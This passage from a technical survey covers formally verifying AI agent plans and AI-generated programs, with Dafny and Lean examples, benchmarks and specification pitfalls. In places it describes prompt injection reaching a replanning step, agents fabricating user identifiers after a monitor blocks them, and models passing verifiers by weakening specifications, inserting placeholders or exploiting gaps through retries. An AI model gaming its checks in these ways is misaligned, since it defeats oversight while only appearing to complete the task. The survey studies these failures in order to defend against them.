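A plan can also leave a decision to a language model and set conditions on the answer. In one of Soteria's examples, a model chooses flights from a list of search results. The plan requires at least one flight, and every chosen flight must have enough seats for all the passengers. The planner can write these conditions without knowing which flights exist. The verifier assumes the answer meets them when it checks the later steps, and Soteria tests the model's actual answer during the run. If the model repeatedly fails the test, the run stops.

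Unlike CaMeLoT and Soteria, SPA doesn't let the planner repair a rejected plan. It calls the planner once per request, and any failure ends the request, because Girrens and Wang don't want the planner to keep revising an unsafe plan until it passes. That seems stricter than necessary for prompt injection, because the verifier's message depends on the plan, the labels and the policy, none of which has to contain text from an attacker. The rule also makes an honest user's task fail when the planner makes a mistake it could easily correct.

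Problems that arise during the run are harder to handle. Dantas and colleagues report that in the study of customer-service agents that made up user identifiers after being blocked, the monitor stopped up to 94% of unsafe actions, but in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly. The survey rates this evidence as very uncertain because it comes from one study with two open-weight models. Soteria's agents did much better on similar tasks. This may be because the plan showed them a permitted next step, but they also used newer models.

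Another approach steers the agent towards a permitted call instead of blocking a forbidden one. In their survey, Dantas and colleagues describe Agent-C, which checks tool calls against rules about the order of actions as the model writes them, and excludes any continuation that would break those rules. With GPT-5, the share of runs that followed the rules rose from 83.7% to 100%, and task completion from 66.1% to 70.6%. But Agent-C replaces only one call at a time, and the survey lists generating a whole new verified sequence after a violation as an open problem.

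An agent can also stop partway, show the planner what it has found, and ask for a new plan. This is the most flexible method, but it exposes the planner to any instructions an attacker has put in the data. The verifier can check the new plan as strictly as the old one, so the agent still can't break a stated rule. But the attacker can now influence which permitted steps the agent takes, which writing the plan first was meant to prevent.

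## Proving ordinary generated software correct

Soteria, CaMeLoT and SPA rely on a contract or label for each tool and don't examine its code. That code is ordinary software, and language models now write much of it too. Coding agents also produce whole programs that people may run for years. These programs have unbounded loops and changing data structures, which languages for plans deliberately omit, so no checker can decide every case automatically. As in proof-carrying code, the producer has to supply a proof, or enough hints for a solver to find one.

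### What a proof can establish about a program

For a function that returns the largest payment in an array, one useful theorem is that the function never reads outside the array. Almost the same statement works for any program, so nobody has to write a new specification for each function. But the theorem is weak, because a function that always returns 0 also satisfies it.

Functional correctness means that a function computes the right answer. For a function that returns the largest payment, the result must be one of the payments, and no payment may exceed it. Somebody has to write these conditions specifically for that function.

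If an older version of the function exists, a model can instead prove that the new version returns the same result for every array. This proof needs no new specification, but the new version will have any bug that the old one has.

### A loop invariant for a small function

In Dafny, the function and its contract could look like this:

```
method Largest(a: array<int>) returns (m: int)
  requires a.Length > 0
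  ensures forall pos :: 0 <= pos < a.Length ==> a[pos] <= m
  ensures exists pos :: 0 <= pos < a.Length && a[pos] == m
{
  m := a[0];
  var i := 1;
  while i < a.Length
    invariant 1 <= i <= a.Length
    invariant forall pos :: 0 <= pos < i ==> a[pos] <= m
    invariant exists pos :: 0 <= pos < i && a[pos] == m
  {
    if a[i] > m { m := a[i]; }
    i := i + 1;
  }
}
```

The `requires` line is the precondition, the `ensures` lines are the postconditions, and `==>` means "implies". Together, the three loop invariants mean that `m` is the largest of the first `i` items. For the array [3, 5, 4], `m` is 3 when `i` is 1, and 5 when `i` is 2 or 3.

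All three hold at the start, where `i` is 1 and `m` is the first item. To show that a pass through the loop preserves the second one, Dafny has to prove roughly this:

```
no item before position i exceeds m
and  new_m is the larger of m and a[i]
implies  no item before position i + 1 exceeds new_m
```

This is true because `a[i]` is the only additional item, and `new_m` is at least as large. When the loop ends, `i` equals `a.Length`, so the last two invariants become the postconditions.

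The first invariant is enough to prove that every read is inside the array, because the loop body runs only while `i` is less than `a.Length`. The other two are needed only to prove functional correctness. The gap between memory safety and functional correctness is much wider in larger programs. For example, a compression library can be free of memory errors and still compress every input incorrectly.

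### How a model repairs a failed proof

Suppose a model's first draft contains the right code but only the first invariant. Dafny accepts the array reads but reports that it can't prove the postconditions. After the loop, the invariants are Dafny's only information about variables that the loop changes, so it has none about `m`.

The model might respond by copying the first postcondition into the loop:

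```
invariant forall pos :: 0 <= pos < a.Length ==> a[pos] <= m
```

Dafny now reports that this invariant may be false when the loop starts. For the array [3, 5], `m` is 3 at that point, but the second item is larger. The model replaces `a.Length` with `i` and adds the matching invariant for the other postcondition. Dafny then accepts the function.

If the model had written `a[i] < m` in the comparison, Dafny would have reported that the loop doesn't preserve the second invariant. It gives the same report when the code is right but the invariant is too weak. *Agentic Verified Optimization of Real-World Software* (Ye, Ghai et al., 2026) points out that a failed proof doesn't tell an agent whether the program is wrong or the proof is incomplete. The agent therefore has to decide whether to work on the program or the proof.

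Kleppmann (2025), in *Prediction*, considers proof scripts one of the best uses of language models, because the checker rejects any hallucinated proof. But the model must be prevented from passing the check without proving the intended property, for example by weakening a postcondition or using Lean's `sorry`, a placeholder for a missing proof. In the experiments of Yao (2026), in *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search*, the software inserts the model's text only into marked gaps in the original specification and rejects any submission that contains `sorry`, a new axiom or a link to outside code.

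### Why models did better with Dafny than with Lean

In Dafny, the model writes annotations and an SMT solver looks for a proof. Verus works in much the same way for Rust programs. Using these tools still takes skill. Dafny's *The Cost of Bugs and of Verification* (2025) notes that most software developers have never learned the logic that loop invariants require.

In Lean, the model has to write the proof too. It can use automated tactics, but it often needs the exact name of a lemma from Mathlib, which has more than 210,000 theorems. A step that a solver completes automatically may take several lines of Lean.

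Benchmarks from 2025 reflect this difference. In the vericoding benchmark, a model receives a formal specification and must write a program with a proof that it meets the specification. The benchmark has more than 12,000 problems, and the success rates reported at its release were 82% in Dafny, 44% in Verus and 27% in Lean. The problems differ between the three languages, so the rates allow only a rough comparison of the tools.

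Two smaller benchmarks from the same year use Lean alone. Verina has 189 programming tasks, and the best general-purpose model at first completed fewer than 5% of the proofs in a single attempt. CLEVER has 161 problems, and the model must also write each specification and prove that it matches a hidden one. Early systems completed almost none of these problems from start to finish.

### Yao's agent loop and tree search

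Those Lean scores are far out of date. Yao tested newer models on 423 Lean problems from the vericoding benchmark, including all of Verina's tasks but none of CLEVER's. One set of 62 problems involves arithmetic on very large numbers like those used in cryptography.

| Method | Model | Problems solved |
|---|---|---|
| Original method, 2025 | GPT-5 | 22.5% |
| Original method, five attempts | GPT-5.4 | 24.6% |
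| Agent loop, 10 model calls | GPT-5.4 | 60.3% |
| Agent loop, 50 model calls | GPT-5.4 | 95.0% |

The original method shows the model its last failed program and Lean's error messages, but none of its earlier attempts. Yao also had to switch off the model's step-by-step reasoning to compare models fairly. The agent loop restores the reasoning, keeps the whole conversation and lets the model search Mathlib. Yao introduced these changes together, so the results don't show which mattered most.

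The newer model gained only two percentage points with the old method, so most of the improvement came from how Yao used the model. Allowing more calls also helped a great deal. With 10 calls, GPT-5.4 solved only 19.4% of the large-number problems. These runs cost about 15 cents per problem, assuming ideal caching of repeated text.

Yao then tried to use the calls more effectively through tree search, in which a parent agent explores several approaches instead of one. One version branches from partial proofs, so several agents can continue the same unfinished proof. The other branches from an agent's entire conversation, which also preserves what that agent learned from its failures. Branching from conversations solved a wider range of moderately difficult problems with fewer tokens. On the hardest problems, a single agent working without interruption did better.

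A score of 95% leaves little room for improvement on the benchmark, whose problems are single functions with specifications already written. Yao concludes that the field needs harder tests based on modern code.

### LeetProof: testing, solving and proving in one tool

A model can use both a solver and a proof assistant. *Certified Program Synthesis with a Multi-Modal Verifier* (Feng, Kurin and colleagues, 2026) presents LeetProof, a pipeline built on Velvet, a verifier inside Lean. Velvet programs have loops and invariants like Dafny's, and a theorem in Lean establishes that the verification conditions imply correctness.

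In one Velvet example, a program checks whether a number `n` is not prime by trying divisors from 2 up to the square root of `n`. The specification counts all the divisors of `n`. Velvet produces 15 verification conditions, and solvers and Lean's automatic tactics prove 14 of them. The remaining condition is that a number above 1 is prime exactly when it has no divisor between 2 and its square root. A person or an AI prover can supply that proof in Lean.

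LeetProof starts from a description in English. A model writes a specification and about ten test cases, and LeetProof uses random testing to look for faults before any code exists. (The same method revealed that about 10% of the reference specifications in the Verina and CLEVER benchmarks are defective, so a high score on them doesn't always mean the programs work as intended.) The model then writes the program and its invariants. LeetProof uses random testing here too, because running a program on a few hundred inputs can expose a bad invariant with much less effort than a failed proof. Solvers prove the routine conditions, and an AI prover attempts the rest.

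On 50 programming problems with loops, LeetProof produced significantly more fully proved solutions than a pipeline that used ordinary Lean proofs with the same budget. This held with two language models. When LeetProof left a program partly proved, Feng and colleagues could finish the proof with more interactive work, so those programs were correct and their proofs were incomplete only because the budget had run out.

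### Using the old program as the specification

Ye and colleagues avoid writing specifications by asking agents to make existing programs faster. Tests are a poor safeguard for this task because an agent can raise its score by skipping work that the tests don't check. Ye and colleagues cite an audit that found errors in 39.5% of the GPU programs that one automated optimisation system had accepted.

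In their method, the agent must supply a faster function and a Lean proof that it equals the old one on every input. One of the old functions finds the length of the longest increasing subsequence of a list. For each number it tries both including it and leaving it out, so an increasing list of 30 numbers leads to about a billion branches. The agent's version fills in a table from the end of the list and needs only a few hundred comparisons. The theorem is short:

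```
theorem lis_equiv (nums : List Int) :
    lisOptimized nums = lisOriginal nums
```

The proof was the hard part, because the old function has no table. The agent connected the two versions with a lemma that, for every tail of the list and every number that might come before it, looking up the answer in the table gives the same result as the old recursion. The new version ran more than 4,000 times faster.

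Agents can also specialise a function. Suppose a faster method works only on sorted lists. The agent proves that this method returns the same results as the old function on sorted lists, then writes a new function that checks whether the list is sorted, using the faster method if it is and the old code if it isn't. The new function returns the same result as the original for every list.

For 156 of Verina's 189 reference programs, agents found a faster version that was proved correct. The median speedup across all 189 was only about 12%. The largest was more than 100,000-fold and came from replacing a repeated sum with a formula.

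For complete applications, Ye and colleagues had agents translate programs from C, C++, Go and Rust into Lean. The agents then optimised 17 of the translations, producing 92 proved rewrites. The optimised applications ran faster than the unoptimised translations in 47 of 51 test scenarios, with an average speedup of 12% across all 51. But they still ran at about one seventh of the speed of the original programs. The proofs start from the Lean translations, and only tests check that those translations match the original programs. The method also excludes effects that are opaque to Lean, such as reading files.

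### How Anthropic and Theorem turned fuzz tests into theorems

Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes a project with Theorem, a formal verification firm, that worked on 123 existing open-source libraries in their original languages. An earlier Theorem project, *lf-lean*, used software to generate the correctness specifications for 1,276 translations from Rocq to Lean, so no person had to define "correct" for each one. Theorem estimates that the verification alone would have taken people about two and a half years of labour.

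The new project took its specifications from fuzz tests. A fuzz test is a small program that passes a sequence of bytes, such as the contents of a supposed image file, to a library. A tool called a fuzzer runs the test on huge numbers of generated inputs and checks for crashes. All 123 libraries come from OSS-Fuzz, a Google service that runs such tests on open-source software.

A fuzz test already contains most of a theorem. It fixes which functions to call and how, and its assertions record what the programmer expected to be true. Anthropic and Theorem only had to replace "the inputs that the fuzzer tried" with "every input":

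```
for every input shorter than 64 MB,
  running the compiled test on that input ends normally,
  with no crash, memory error or failed assertion
```

The number of such inputs has more than 150 million digits, so no fuzzer could ever try them all.

Claude wrote the proofs in Rocq, and Rocq's kernel checked them. The proofs cover the machine instructions that a compiler produced for RISC-V, a family of processors with a relatively simple instruction set, so a bug that the compiler introduced would show up in the proof. The project defines "running" using a mathematical model of the processor and the parts of Linux that the program needs, with a fixed amount of memory. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) explains that each program in the model is single-threaded and static (all the code it uses is in one file).

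The project took a few weeks and covered 239 fuzz tests. The proofs total about 180 million lines, according to a Russian account, OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026). A binary with 18,000 instructions needs about 600,000 lines of proof, or more than 30 lines per instruction. Nobody will read proofs this long, but that doesn't matter if the kernel accepts them and the theorem is the right one.

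Trying to prove the programs correct also exposed bugs. If a program can write past the end of a buffer, no proof exists, and the failed step points to the code responsible. OpenNET reports that Claude found and fixed hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed, including a buffer overflow in libexpat, a widely used XML parsing library, and errors in the programs' logic. When a library needed a fix, the theorem applies to the corrected code, so it doesn't protect anyone still running the old version.

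The guarantee covers only the code that a test reaches. The theorem may not apply if an application calls a function that no fuzz test uses, or calls the tested functions in a different order. The guarantee also excludes threads, code loaded from separate files at run time, and faulty hardware. Claude could not prove every target. Anthropic is publishing the specifications for the unproven ones, along with proofs for the programs that needed no changes, and has invited others to check the work.

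Claude also proved stronger properties of two programs. It proved that the Linux kernel's version of zlib, a compression library, conforms to RFC 1950, the published standard for its data format. It also wrote an interpreter for part of the Python language in Rust and used Verus to prove that the interpreter follows a formal description of Python. The standard Python interpreter has no such description, so the project compared the two interpreters on 1.7 million random programs. They agreed on 99.95%, and the disagreements were known edge cases. Like Ye and colleagues' translations, this proof relies on tests to connect the formal description to the program people actually use.

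### Why seL4 took 20 person-years

The usual example of how much work verification takes is seL4, a small operating-system kernel first proved correct in 2009. According to *AI Could Make Formal Verification Economically Viable at Scale* (2025), verifying its 8,700 lines of C took 20 person-years and 200,000 lines of proof. The 123 libraries took only a few weeks, but the two times are not directly comparable because the theorems are very different.

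| | seL4 | Anthropic and Theorem |
|---|---|---|
| Software | One operating-system kernel | 239 test programs from 123 libraries |
| Code in the theorem | C source code | Compiled RISC-V instructions |
| Main property | The kernel does what its specification describes | The test programs don't crash |
| Source of the specification | Experts wrote it for seL4 | Existing fuzz tests |
| Length of proof | 200,000 lines | About 180 million lines |
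| Effort | 20 person-years | A few weeks |

The seL4 team proved functional correctness. Their specification describes the effect of each request a program can make to the kernel, and the proof shows that the C code has that effect. They had to decide what the kernel should do in every situation, and then find invariants that relate all its data structures to one another. For most of the 123 libraries, by contrast, a version that read its input and did nothing with it would satisfy the theorem, unless an assertion in the fuzz test happened to rule it out.

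The effort figures also measure different things. The twenty person-years are labour, much of it by people who were developing the methods as they went, while the few weeks are calendar time for a project whose announcement has 15 authors. The few weeks also exclude the computing. The new project could build on decades of work on proof assistants and processor models.

The comparison isn't entirely in seL4's favour. Its original theorem is about C source code, so its users also had to trust the compiler. A modest theorem about 123 libraries may also prevent more attacks than a deep one about a single kernel, because attackers so often exploit memory errors. The two projects show that proving a given kind of theorem now takes much less effort, but not how much less for a theorem like seL4's.

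### Proofs cost less, but people still choose what to prove

Lean (2026), the organisation behind the proof assistant, describes how Ilya Sergey used Claude to verify the borrow checker of Move, a language for programs that handle digital assets. A borrow checker makes sure that a program doesn't use a value in conflicting ways. The proof has 39,000 lines and took 27 working days, compared with an estimated five to six months without AI. Sergey worked out new proof strategies, while Claude extended existing arguments to new cases and repaired broken proofs. He used Claude Opus 4.5 and 4.6, so current models might need less help with the strategies.

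People also kept control of the specifications in *Agent-Driven Verification of Memory Safety for liblzma Decoder Components with VST* (Shlyakhtun, Gryzlov and colleagues, 2026). Agents proved 22 theorems about parts of liblzma, a decompression library, in 1,595 sessions, or more than 70 per theorem. The theorems cover memory safety and some functional correctness, and they assume contracts for other functions that the components call. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), of the company Runtime Verification, argue more generally in *The proof is in the spec* that as proofs become easier to produce, the main difficulty moves to specifications, models and the choice of assumptions.

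### Keeping proofs up to date

When software changes, its proofs have to change too. If a programmer rewrites `Largest` to search from the end of the array, its contract stays the same, but the invariants must describe the last items instead of the first. Proofs about compiled code are even more sensitive to change, because a new compiler version can produce different instructions from the same source.

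Each new feature used to mean more proof work for scarce experts, which discouraged verification. Models may change that, because much proof repair is routine. In Shlyakhtun and colleagues' project, people approved changes to the specifications and agents updated the proofs to match. This replaces labour with computing, but someone who maintains 600,000 lines of proof for one binary still has to pay to regenerate and recheck them. None of the projects has yet kept proofs on this scale current through years of releases, so the long-term cost is unknown.

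Changing the processor also requires new proofs. Most servers and personal computers don't use RISC-V, and many use x86, whose instruction set is harder to model. In October 2026, Leip announced a proof about the complete run of one x86 program under Linux (*Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*). Zellic and V12 want to turn this into a reusable method, with AI models working under expert guidance.

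### Threads

The restriction to a single thread is harder to remove. Suppose `Largest` has examined the first item of [3, 5, 4], so `m` is 3, and another thread then changes that item to 9. This makes the invariant false, although nothing is wrong with the loop. A proof can rule out such changes, for example by showing that the thread holds a lock on the array. Otherwise it has to cover every order in which the threads' steps can occur, and two threads with ten steps each have 184,756 possible orders.

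Agents have helped with proofs of this kind too. *Formal Verification of an Out-of-Order Multiprocessor against an In-Order Weak-Memory ISA* (2026) covers a processor design whose cores share memory and may run instructions out of order. It proves that, for any number of cores, programs can't observe any behaviour that a simpler, in-order design wouldn't allow. Agents wrote most of the proof scripts. They also found a mistake in the specification of the out-of-order processor, gave examples of the forbidden behaviour and proposed the right correction. But when an agent added instructions that read and change memory in one step, it at first recorded each write at the wrong time. The researchers reviewed about 500 lines of generated definitions by hand, because a proof can't reveal that a definition describes the wrong machine.

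### Writing programs that are easier to prove

Programmers can make a proof easier by designing the program with the proof in mind. Mascherbauer and Aichernig (2026), in *A Verified Implementation of the L\*-Algorithm in Lean*, did this for an algorithm that infers the rules of an unknown system from the answers to queries about it. They wanted to use Mathlib's theorems about sets, but a set in Mathlib is only a condition that each item either meets or doesn't, so a program can't go through its members one by one. They therefore stored the symbols in a list, with a proof that the list contains every symbol exactly once. This lets the program run through the list while the proofs treat it as a finite set.

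Such choices often make programs slower, because the data structures that are easiest to reason about are rarely the fastest. Verified optimisation addresses this by starting with a simple version that is proved correct, then having an agent replace it with a faster one that it proves equivalent. This order of work seems sensible for new software. The results of Ye and colleagues suggest that moving existing software to Lean still slows it down too much, but proofs about its compiled code don't require the move.

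## Whether the specification says what was meant

A proof shows that a program meets its specification, but not that the specification matches what someone wanted. Meijer illustrates this with a deletion tool that accepts patterns, in which `*` stands for any text. A user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The model writes a one-step plan, `delete_file("*.txt")`, which is shorter than deleting the files one by one.

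### Deleting two files and nothing else

Suppose the folder also contains `notes.txt` and `photo.png`. The simplest specifications for the tool and the task are:

```
delete_file(pattern)
  ensures  every file that matches the pattern is gone

the task
  ensures  foo.txt is gone and bar.txt is gone
```

Both files match `*.txt`, so the tool's postcondition implies the task's, and a verifier accepts the plan. The plan also deletes `notes.txt`, which neither postcondition prohibits. Meijer doesn't blame the model, because its plan meets the specification.

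He traces the mistake to the frame problem, which John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes described in 1969: a description of what an action changes leaves open what stays the same. His remedy is to add a frame condition to the tool:

```
  ensures  every file that does not match the pattern
           exists afterwards exactly if it existed before
```

Meijer concludes that the `*.txt` plan now fails to verify, but in fact it still passes. The new condition protects `photo.png`, which doesn't match the pattern, but not `notes.txt`, which does. A stronger postcondition for a tool gives the verifier an extra fact to use in its proofs, so in principle it can only lead to more accepted plans, never fewer. To exclude the bad plan, the task needs a frame condition of its own:

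```
  ensures  every file other than foo.txt and bar.txt
           exists afterwards exactly if it existed before
```

| Condition | True after deleting `*.txt`? |
|---|---|
| Tool: matching files are gone | Yes |
| Tool: other files are unchanged | Yes, `photo.png` is still there |
| Task: `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` are gone | Yes |
| Task: all other files are unchanged | No, `notes.txt` is gone |

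The tool's frame condition is still necessary, because without it the verifier would reject good plans too. Suppose the model deletes `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` in two steps. To prove that `notes.txt` survives, the verifier needs a guarantee that deleting `foo.txt` affects no other file.

### Kinds of faulty specification

Every program meets a vacuous specification, so proving that a program meets one provides no information about the program. *FaithformBench* (Cornish and colleagues, 2026) studies models that translate mathematical reasoning from English into Lean. A faithful translation of a wrong step is a false statement, so if Lean can prove the translation, the translator has changed the meaning. In one wrong step, 3^x = 5 supposedly implies 3^(x+2) = 51, although the right answer is 45. A translator called Kimina declared `x` to be a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3^x =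 5, so the implication is trivially true. According to Tolmach and Klaus, all the specially trained translators in the study made silent changes like this, and the ones that were best at translating correct statements made them most often. A contract with a precondition that no input satisfies is vacuous in the same way.

A specification can also be meaningful but too weak. *Intent Formalization* (Lahiri, 2026) gives the example of a function that returns the common elements of two arrays. GPT-4 wrote a specification that required every item in the result to be in both arrays and prohibited duplicates. Expert reviewers labelled it "strong", but a function that always returns an empty list satisfies it. An automated test found the gap by replacing correct outputs with wrong ones and checking whether the specification rejected them. The corrected version requires an item to be in the result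 if and only if it is in both arrays.

If a task's postcondition contradicts itself, no plan can pass, and people soon notice. A contradiction among the verifier's assumptions is more dangerous, because any claim, even a false one, follows from it. Suppose a programmer writes the deletion tool's frame condition as "every file is unchanged" and forgets to exclude the matching files. After a call that deletes an existing file, the verifier would assume that the file is both gone and still there. It could then prove any claim about the rest of the plan, including that the plan sends no mail. Soteria's check that the facts at each state are satisfiable would detect the contradiction.

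Sometimes the proof is about a simplified model of the program. Tolmach and Klaus describe a test in which Claude had to model Etcd, a database that keeps several computers in agreement using an algorithm called Raft. Claude produced essentially the model from the appendix of the Raft paper, which passed every check but reflected little of Etcd's code. In the same benchmark, specifications written by leading language models scored nearly 100% for syntax and about 46% for agreement with the real code. Tolmach and Klaus recommend translating code by fixed rules instead of with a language model. An easier check is to run the simplified model and the original program on the same generated inputs and compare the results.

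A model that adds contracts to existing code may also change the code. In *An Empirical Study of LLM-Generated Specifications for VeriFast* (2026), at least two researchers therefore compared each function before and after the model edited it, and recorded whether the model had changed the code or weakened the function's contract.

Finally, a specification may leave out an effect. Even the corrected specification for the deletion task covers only which files exist, so a plan with access to a writing tool could delete the right two files and then erase the text of `notes.txt`. Adding file contents to the frame condition would prevent this, but would still allow the plan to send an email. Requiring that nothing else change is too strict, because even a well-behaved tool may write to a log, so somebody has to decide which changes matter.

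### Why retries find the gaps

Gaps in a specification matter more when a model can retry until the verifier accepts a plan. Suppose each attempt has a 20% chance of producing a correct plan that passes and a 1% chance of producing a wrong plan that passes because of a gap. With a single attempt, the verifier accepts a wrong plan for 1% of requests. If the model retries until a plan passes, this share rises to 1 in 21, or almost 5%.

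Accepted plans are more likely to be wrong when the task is difficult. If each attempt has a 1% chance of producing a right plan and a 1% chance of producing a wrong plan that passes, half of the accepted plans are wrong. If the policy makes the task impossible, every accepted plan is wrong, and 50 attempts still have about a 40% chance of producing one. This can happen without the model intending to cheat, because the checker selects any plan that passes. A plan that passes after many failures deserves more suspicion than one that passes immediately, because the failures suggest that right plans are rare.

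These figures assume the attempts are independent. In practice, the model usually sees the verifier's error messages, which can help it correct mistakes but can also lead it to a gap in the specification.

The risk grows if the model writes the specification too, because weakening a postcondition is often easier than fixing a program. Counting only the programs a verifier accepts can then favor a system that writes more postconditions that are always true. *VerusEval* (Wang, Jiang et al., 2026) compared systems that generate Verus contracts and proofs for Rust programs. Using GPT-4o, an adapted version of AutoVerus got 77.0% of its programs past the verifier, and StarVerus got 73.4%. But only 87.4% of AutoVerus's contracts passed a check that rejects always-true postconditions, compared with 99.6% of StarVerus's.

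### Clover's consistency checks

*Clover* (Sun, Sheng and colleagues, 2023) looks for faulty specifications by comparing a function's code, its contract and an English comment. Dafny checks that the code meets the contract. In each of five other checks, GPT-4 reconstructs one of the three from another alone, and Clover tests whether the reconstruction matches the original.

Dafny would still accept the function `Largest` from the previous section if its contract required only that no item exceed the result. But if GPT-4 wrote a new contract from the comment "Returns the largest item in the array", it would probably also require the result to be one of the items. Dafny could not then prove the two contracts equivalent, so Clover would reject the function.

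Sun and colleagues tested Clover on 60 textbook programs, each with four faulty versions that still passed Dafny. Clover accepted 45 of the 60 correct programs and rejected all 240 faulty ones. When it repeated each check up to ten times and counted any success as a pass, it accepted 52 correct programs and still no faulty ones.

Most of the checks are unreliable on their own. When the contract was too weak, reconstructing the code from it exposed the fault in only 26 of 60 cases, perhaps because GPT-4 can often guess what a function is for. Individual checks also catch fewer faults when they are repeated. When the comment and contract were both too weak, reconstructing the contract from the comment exposed the fault in 44 of 60 programs with one try but only 30 with ten.

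Sun and colleagues acknowledge that Clover cannot detect an edge case that the code, contract and comment all omit. The deletion example is close to such a case. From the comment "Delete foo.txt and bar.txt", a model might well reconstruct the same incomplete postcondition. Reconstructed code would probably delete the files separately, but Clover compares programs by running them on a few inputs, so it would detect a difference only if one of the test folders contained another text file. Clover also needs a comment that determines a single result for every input, and few requests to an agent are that precise.

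### Astrogator's readable queries

Another approach is to have the user check the specification. Councilman, Fu and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Formal Verification of LLM-Generated Code from Natural Language Prompts*, designed a formal language that resembles English. Their system, Astrogator, checks programs in Ansible, a language for setting up and managing remote computers. A request to move a file becomes this query:

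```
move file from remote "/scratch/file.txt"
          to remote "/home/user/data.txt"
```

"Remote" means the managed computer, as opposed to the controller, which sends it commands. The user is supposed to read the query and confirm it. A knowledge base supplies technical details, such as each operating system's name for a software package, so the user doesn't have to know them. Astrogator then works out what the program would change from each possible starting state and checks that these changes include everything in the query.

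In the evaluation, six language models each wrote ten programs per task for 21 tasks, and 334 of the 1,260 programs were correct. Astrogator verified 277 of the correct programs (83%) and rejected 856 of the 926 incorrect ones (92%). Because most of the programs were incorrect, about one in five of the programs it accepted was wrong.

One task accounts for 49 of the 70 wrongly accepted programs. The user wanted to copy a file within the remote computer, but the programs copied it from the controller. Astrogator accepted them because the result is right if the controller has a file with the same contents. Astrogator can list such assumptions for the user to approve, but the evaluation left out that step. With it, a careful user might have caught most of these errors.

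Seven other programs did more than the query asked. Some overwrote a file every time when the task was to create it only if it didn't exist, and some always restarted a computer when the task was to restart it if necessary. Astrogator allows extra actions on purpose, because a program may have to install Git, for example, before it can copy a repository. Councilman and colleagues suggest adding a small frame condition by treating "if the file does not exist, create it" as if it continued "otherwise do not modify it".

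The researchers wrote all the queries themselves, so the evaluation doesn't show whether a language model can translate requests into queries or whether users notice when a query is wrong.

Users may find examples easier to judge than rules. Lahiri describes TiCoder, a system that looks for inputs on which several generated programs give different outputs and asks the user about them. If a user wants the shared elements of two lists, TiCoder might ask whether [1, 2, 2] and [2, 2, 3] should give [2, 2]. In a study with 15 professional developers, the share of generated code that they judged correctly rose from 40% to 84%. For the deletion task, a good question would be whether `notes.txt` should still exist afterwards. But if every generated plan deleted `*.txt`, TiCoder would find no difference to ask about.

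### How well models write specifications

*Verus-SpecGym* (Agarwal, Neamtu and colleagues, 2026) shows by example how many ways a short specification can go wrong. A function must return the first position of a number in a sorted array, counting from 0, or -1 if the number isn't there.

| Faulty specification | Consequence |
|---|---|
| The array must be strictly increasing | Excludes [10, 20, 20, 20, 30], a valid input |
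| The array can be in any order | Allows [3, 2, 3], an invalid input |
| The result must be a position of the number | Rejects -1, the right answer when searching the first array for 24 |
| Any position of the number will do | Accepts position 3 for 20 in the first array, although the right answer is 1 |

With the last of these, a verifier could approve a function that gives wrong answers. The strictly increasing precondition is also risky, because a proof that relies on it doesn't cover arrays with repeated numbers.

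The benchmark contains 581 problems from Codeforces, a programming contest site where competitors try to find inputs that break each other's programs. Agarwal and colleagues used those inputs to test the specifications, and a specification passed only if it gave the right verdict on every test. Gemini 3.1 Pro succeeded on 77.8% of the problems, GPT-5.3-Codex on 57.8% and Claude Opus 4.6 on 51.1%. Newer models have replaced all three, so these scores are probably out of date.

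The comparison with ordinary programming may hold for longer. Of 187 problems for which GPT-5.3-Codex wrote a wrong specification, it solved 153 when asked for a Python program. It was also unreliable at checking its own work, approving 49 of 191 wrong specifications. The benchmark can miss errors too, since a wrong specification may give the right verdict on every test. Contest problems are also stated much more precisely than most requests for code.

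Wang and colleagues compared generated contracts with reference contracts. This comparison covers all inputs instead of a sample. Of 7,081 programs that Verus had accepted, only 42.3% passed it along with a set of tests and a check for vacuous contracts. The rest weren't all wrong, because a solver may fail to prove that two contracts are equivalent even when they are. In about 24% of the accepted programs, the researchers found firmer evidence of a fault, such as a failed test. Most of the models in this study were older than those that Agarwal and colleagues tested.

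The references had faults as well. Wang and colleagues selected 61 suspicious ones for review, and 36 appeared to be defective. One, for a function that returns the smallest item in an array, didn't require the result to be in the array. Eleven generated contracts, from five models, included this requirement and therefore failed the comparison. Ten of them passed once the researchers corrected the reference.

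### Do cheap proofs only move the difficulty?

To support their view that specification is the bottleneck, Tolmach and Klaus give the example of a queue shared by several threads. Before anyone can prove the queue correct, somebody has to decide whether "correct" means memory safety, keeping items in order or something else, and whether the proof should allow for memory allocation failing. Their company sells this expertise, but Lahiri, of Microsoft Research, also considers validating specifications the central bottleneck, because only the user can judge whether a specification is right.

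The opposing view is that many useful policies don't depend on the task, so people can write them once and reuse them. Soteria's researchers needed only a few hours to correct the policies and contracts for each domain, and users of proof-carrying completions choose properties from a list. Lahiri supports part of this view, since he recommends partial specifications as lightweight guardrails.

Confidentiality suits reusable policies well. Meijer's rule about private mail applies whatever the user has asked for. However, the rule covers only `body`, so a plan could put the summary in a subject line or an attachment if the mail tool accepts them. A plan could also post the summary to a website with a different tool. Somebody has to list every way for data to leave, but that list grows with the number of tools rather than the number of requests. The rule also blocks some legitimate requests,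 such as sending an invoice from the mailbox to an outside accountant, until somebody writes an exception.

A refund rule takes more thought. Suppose an airline gives refunds to customers who cancel within 24 hours of booking. A simple version of the rule is:

```
cancelled within 24 hours  implies  refunded
```

An agent that refunds everybody satisfies this rule, much as Astrogator accepted programs that always restarted the computer. Reversing the implication would allow an agent that refunds nobody. The rule must therefore state the implication in both directions, like the corrected specification for common elements. It must also specify the refund amount and limit each booking to one refund, because two full refunds could each be correct on their own. The airline still has to settle questions such as whether the 24-hour period begins when the customer books or when the payment arrives,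 but thousands of plans can then use the answers, so the specification work per plan is small.

Neither easier proofs nor reuse helps much with specifying "a safe answer". Meijer notes that what people consider inappropriate varies between cultures. Safety can also depend on who receives the answer, since a dose of medicine that is safe for an adult may be dangerous for a child. A verifier could prove that a plan never shows an answer until a separate model has approved it, but that proof would cover only the order of the calls. The protection would still depend on the approving model's judgment.

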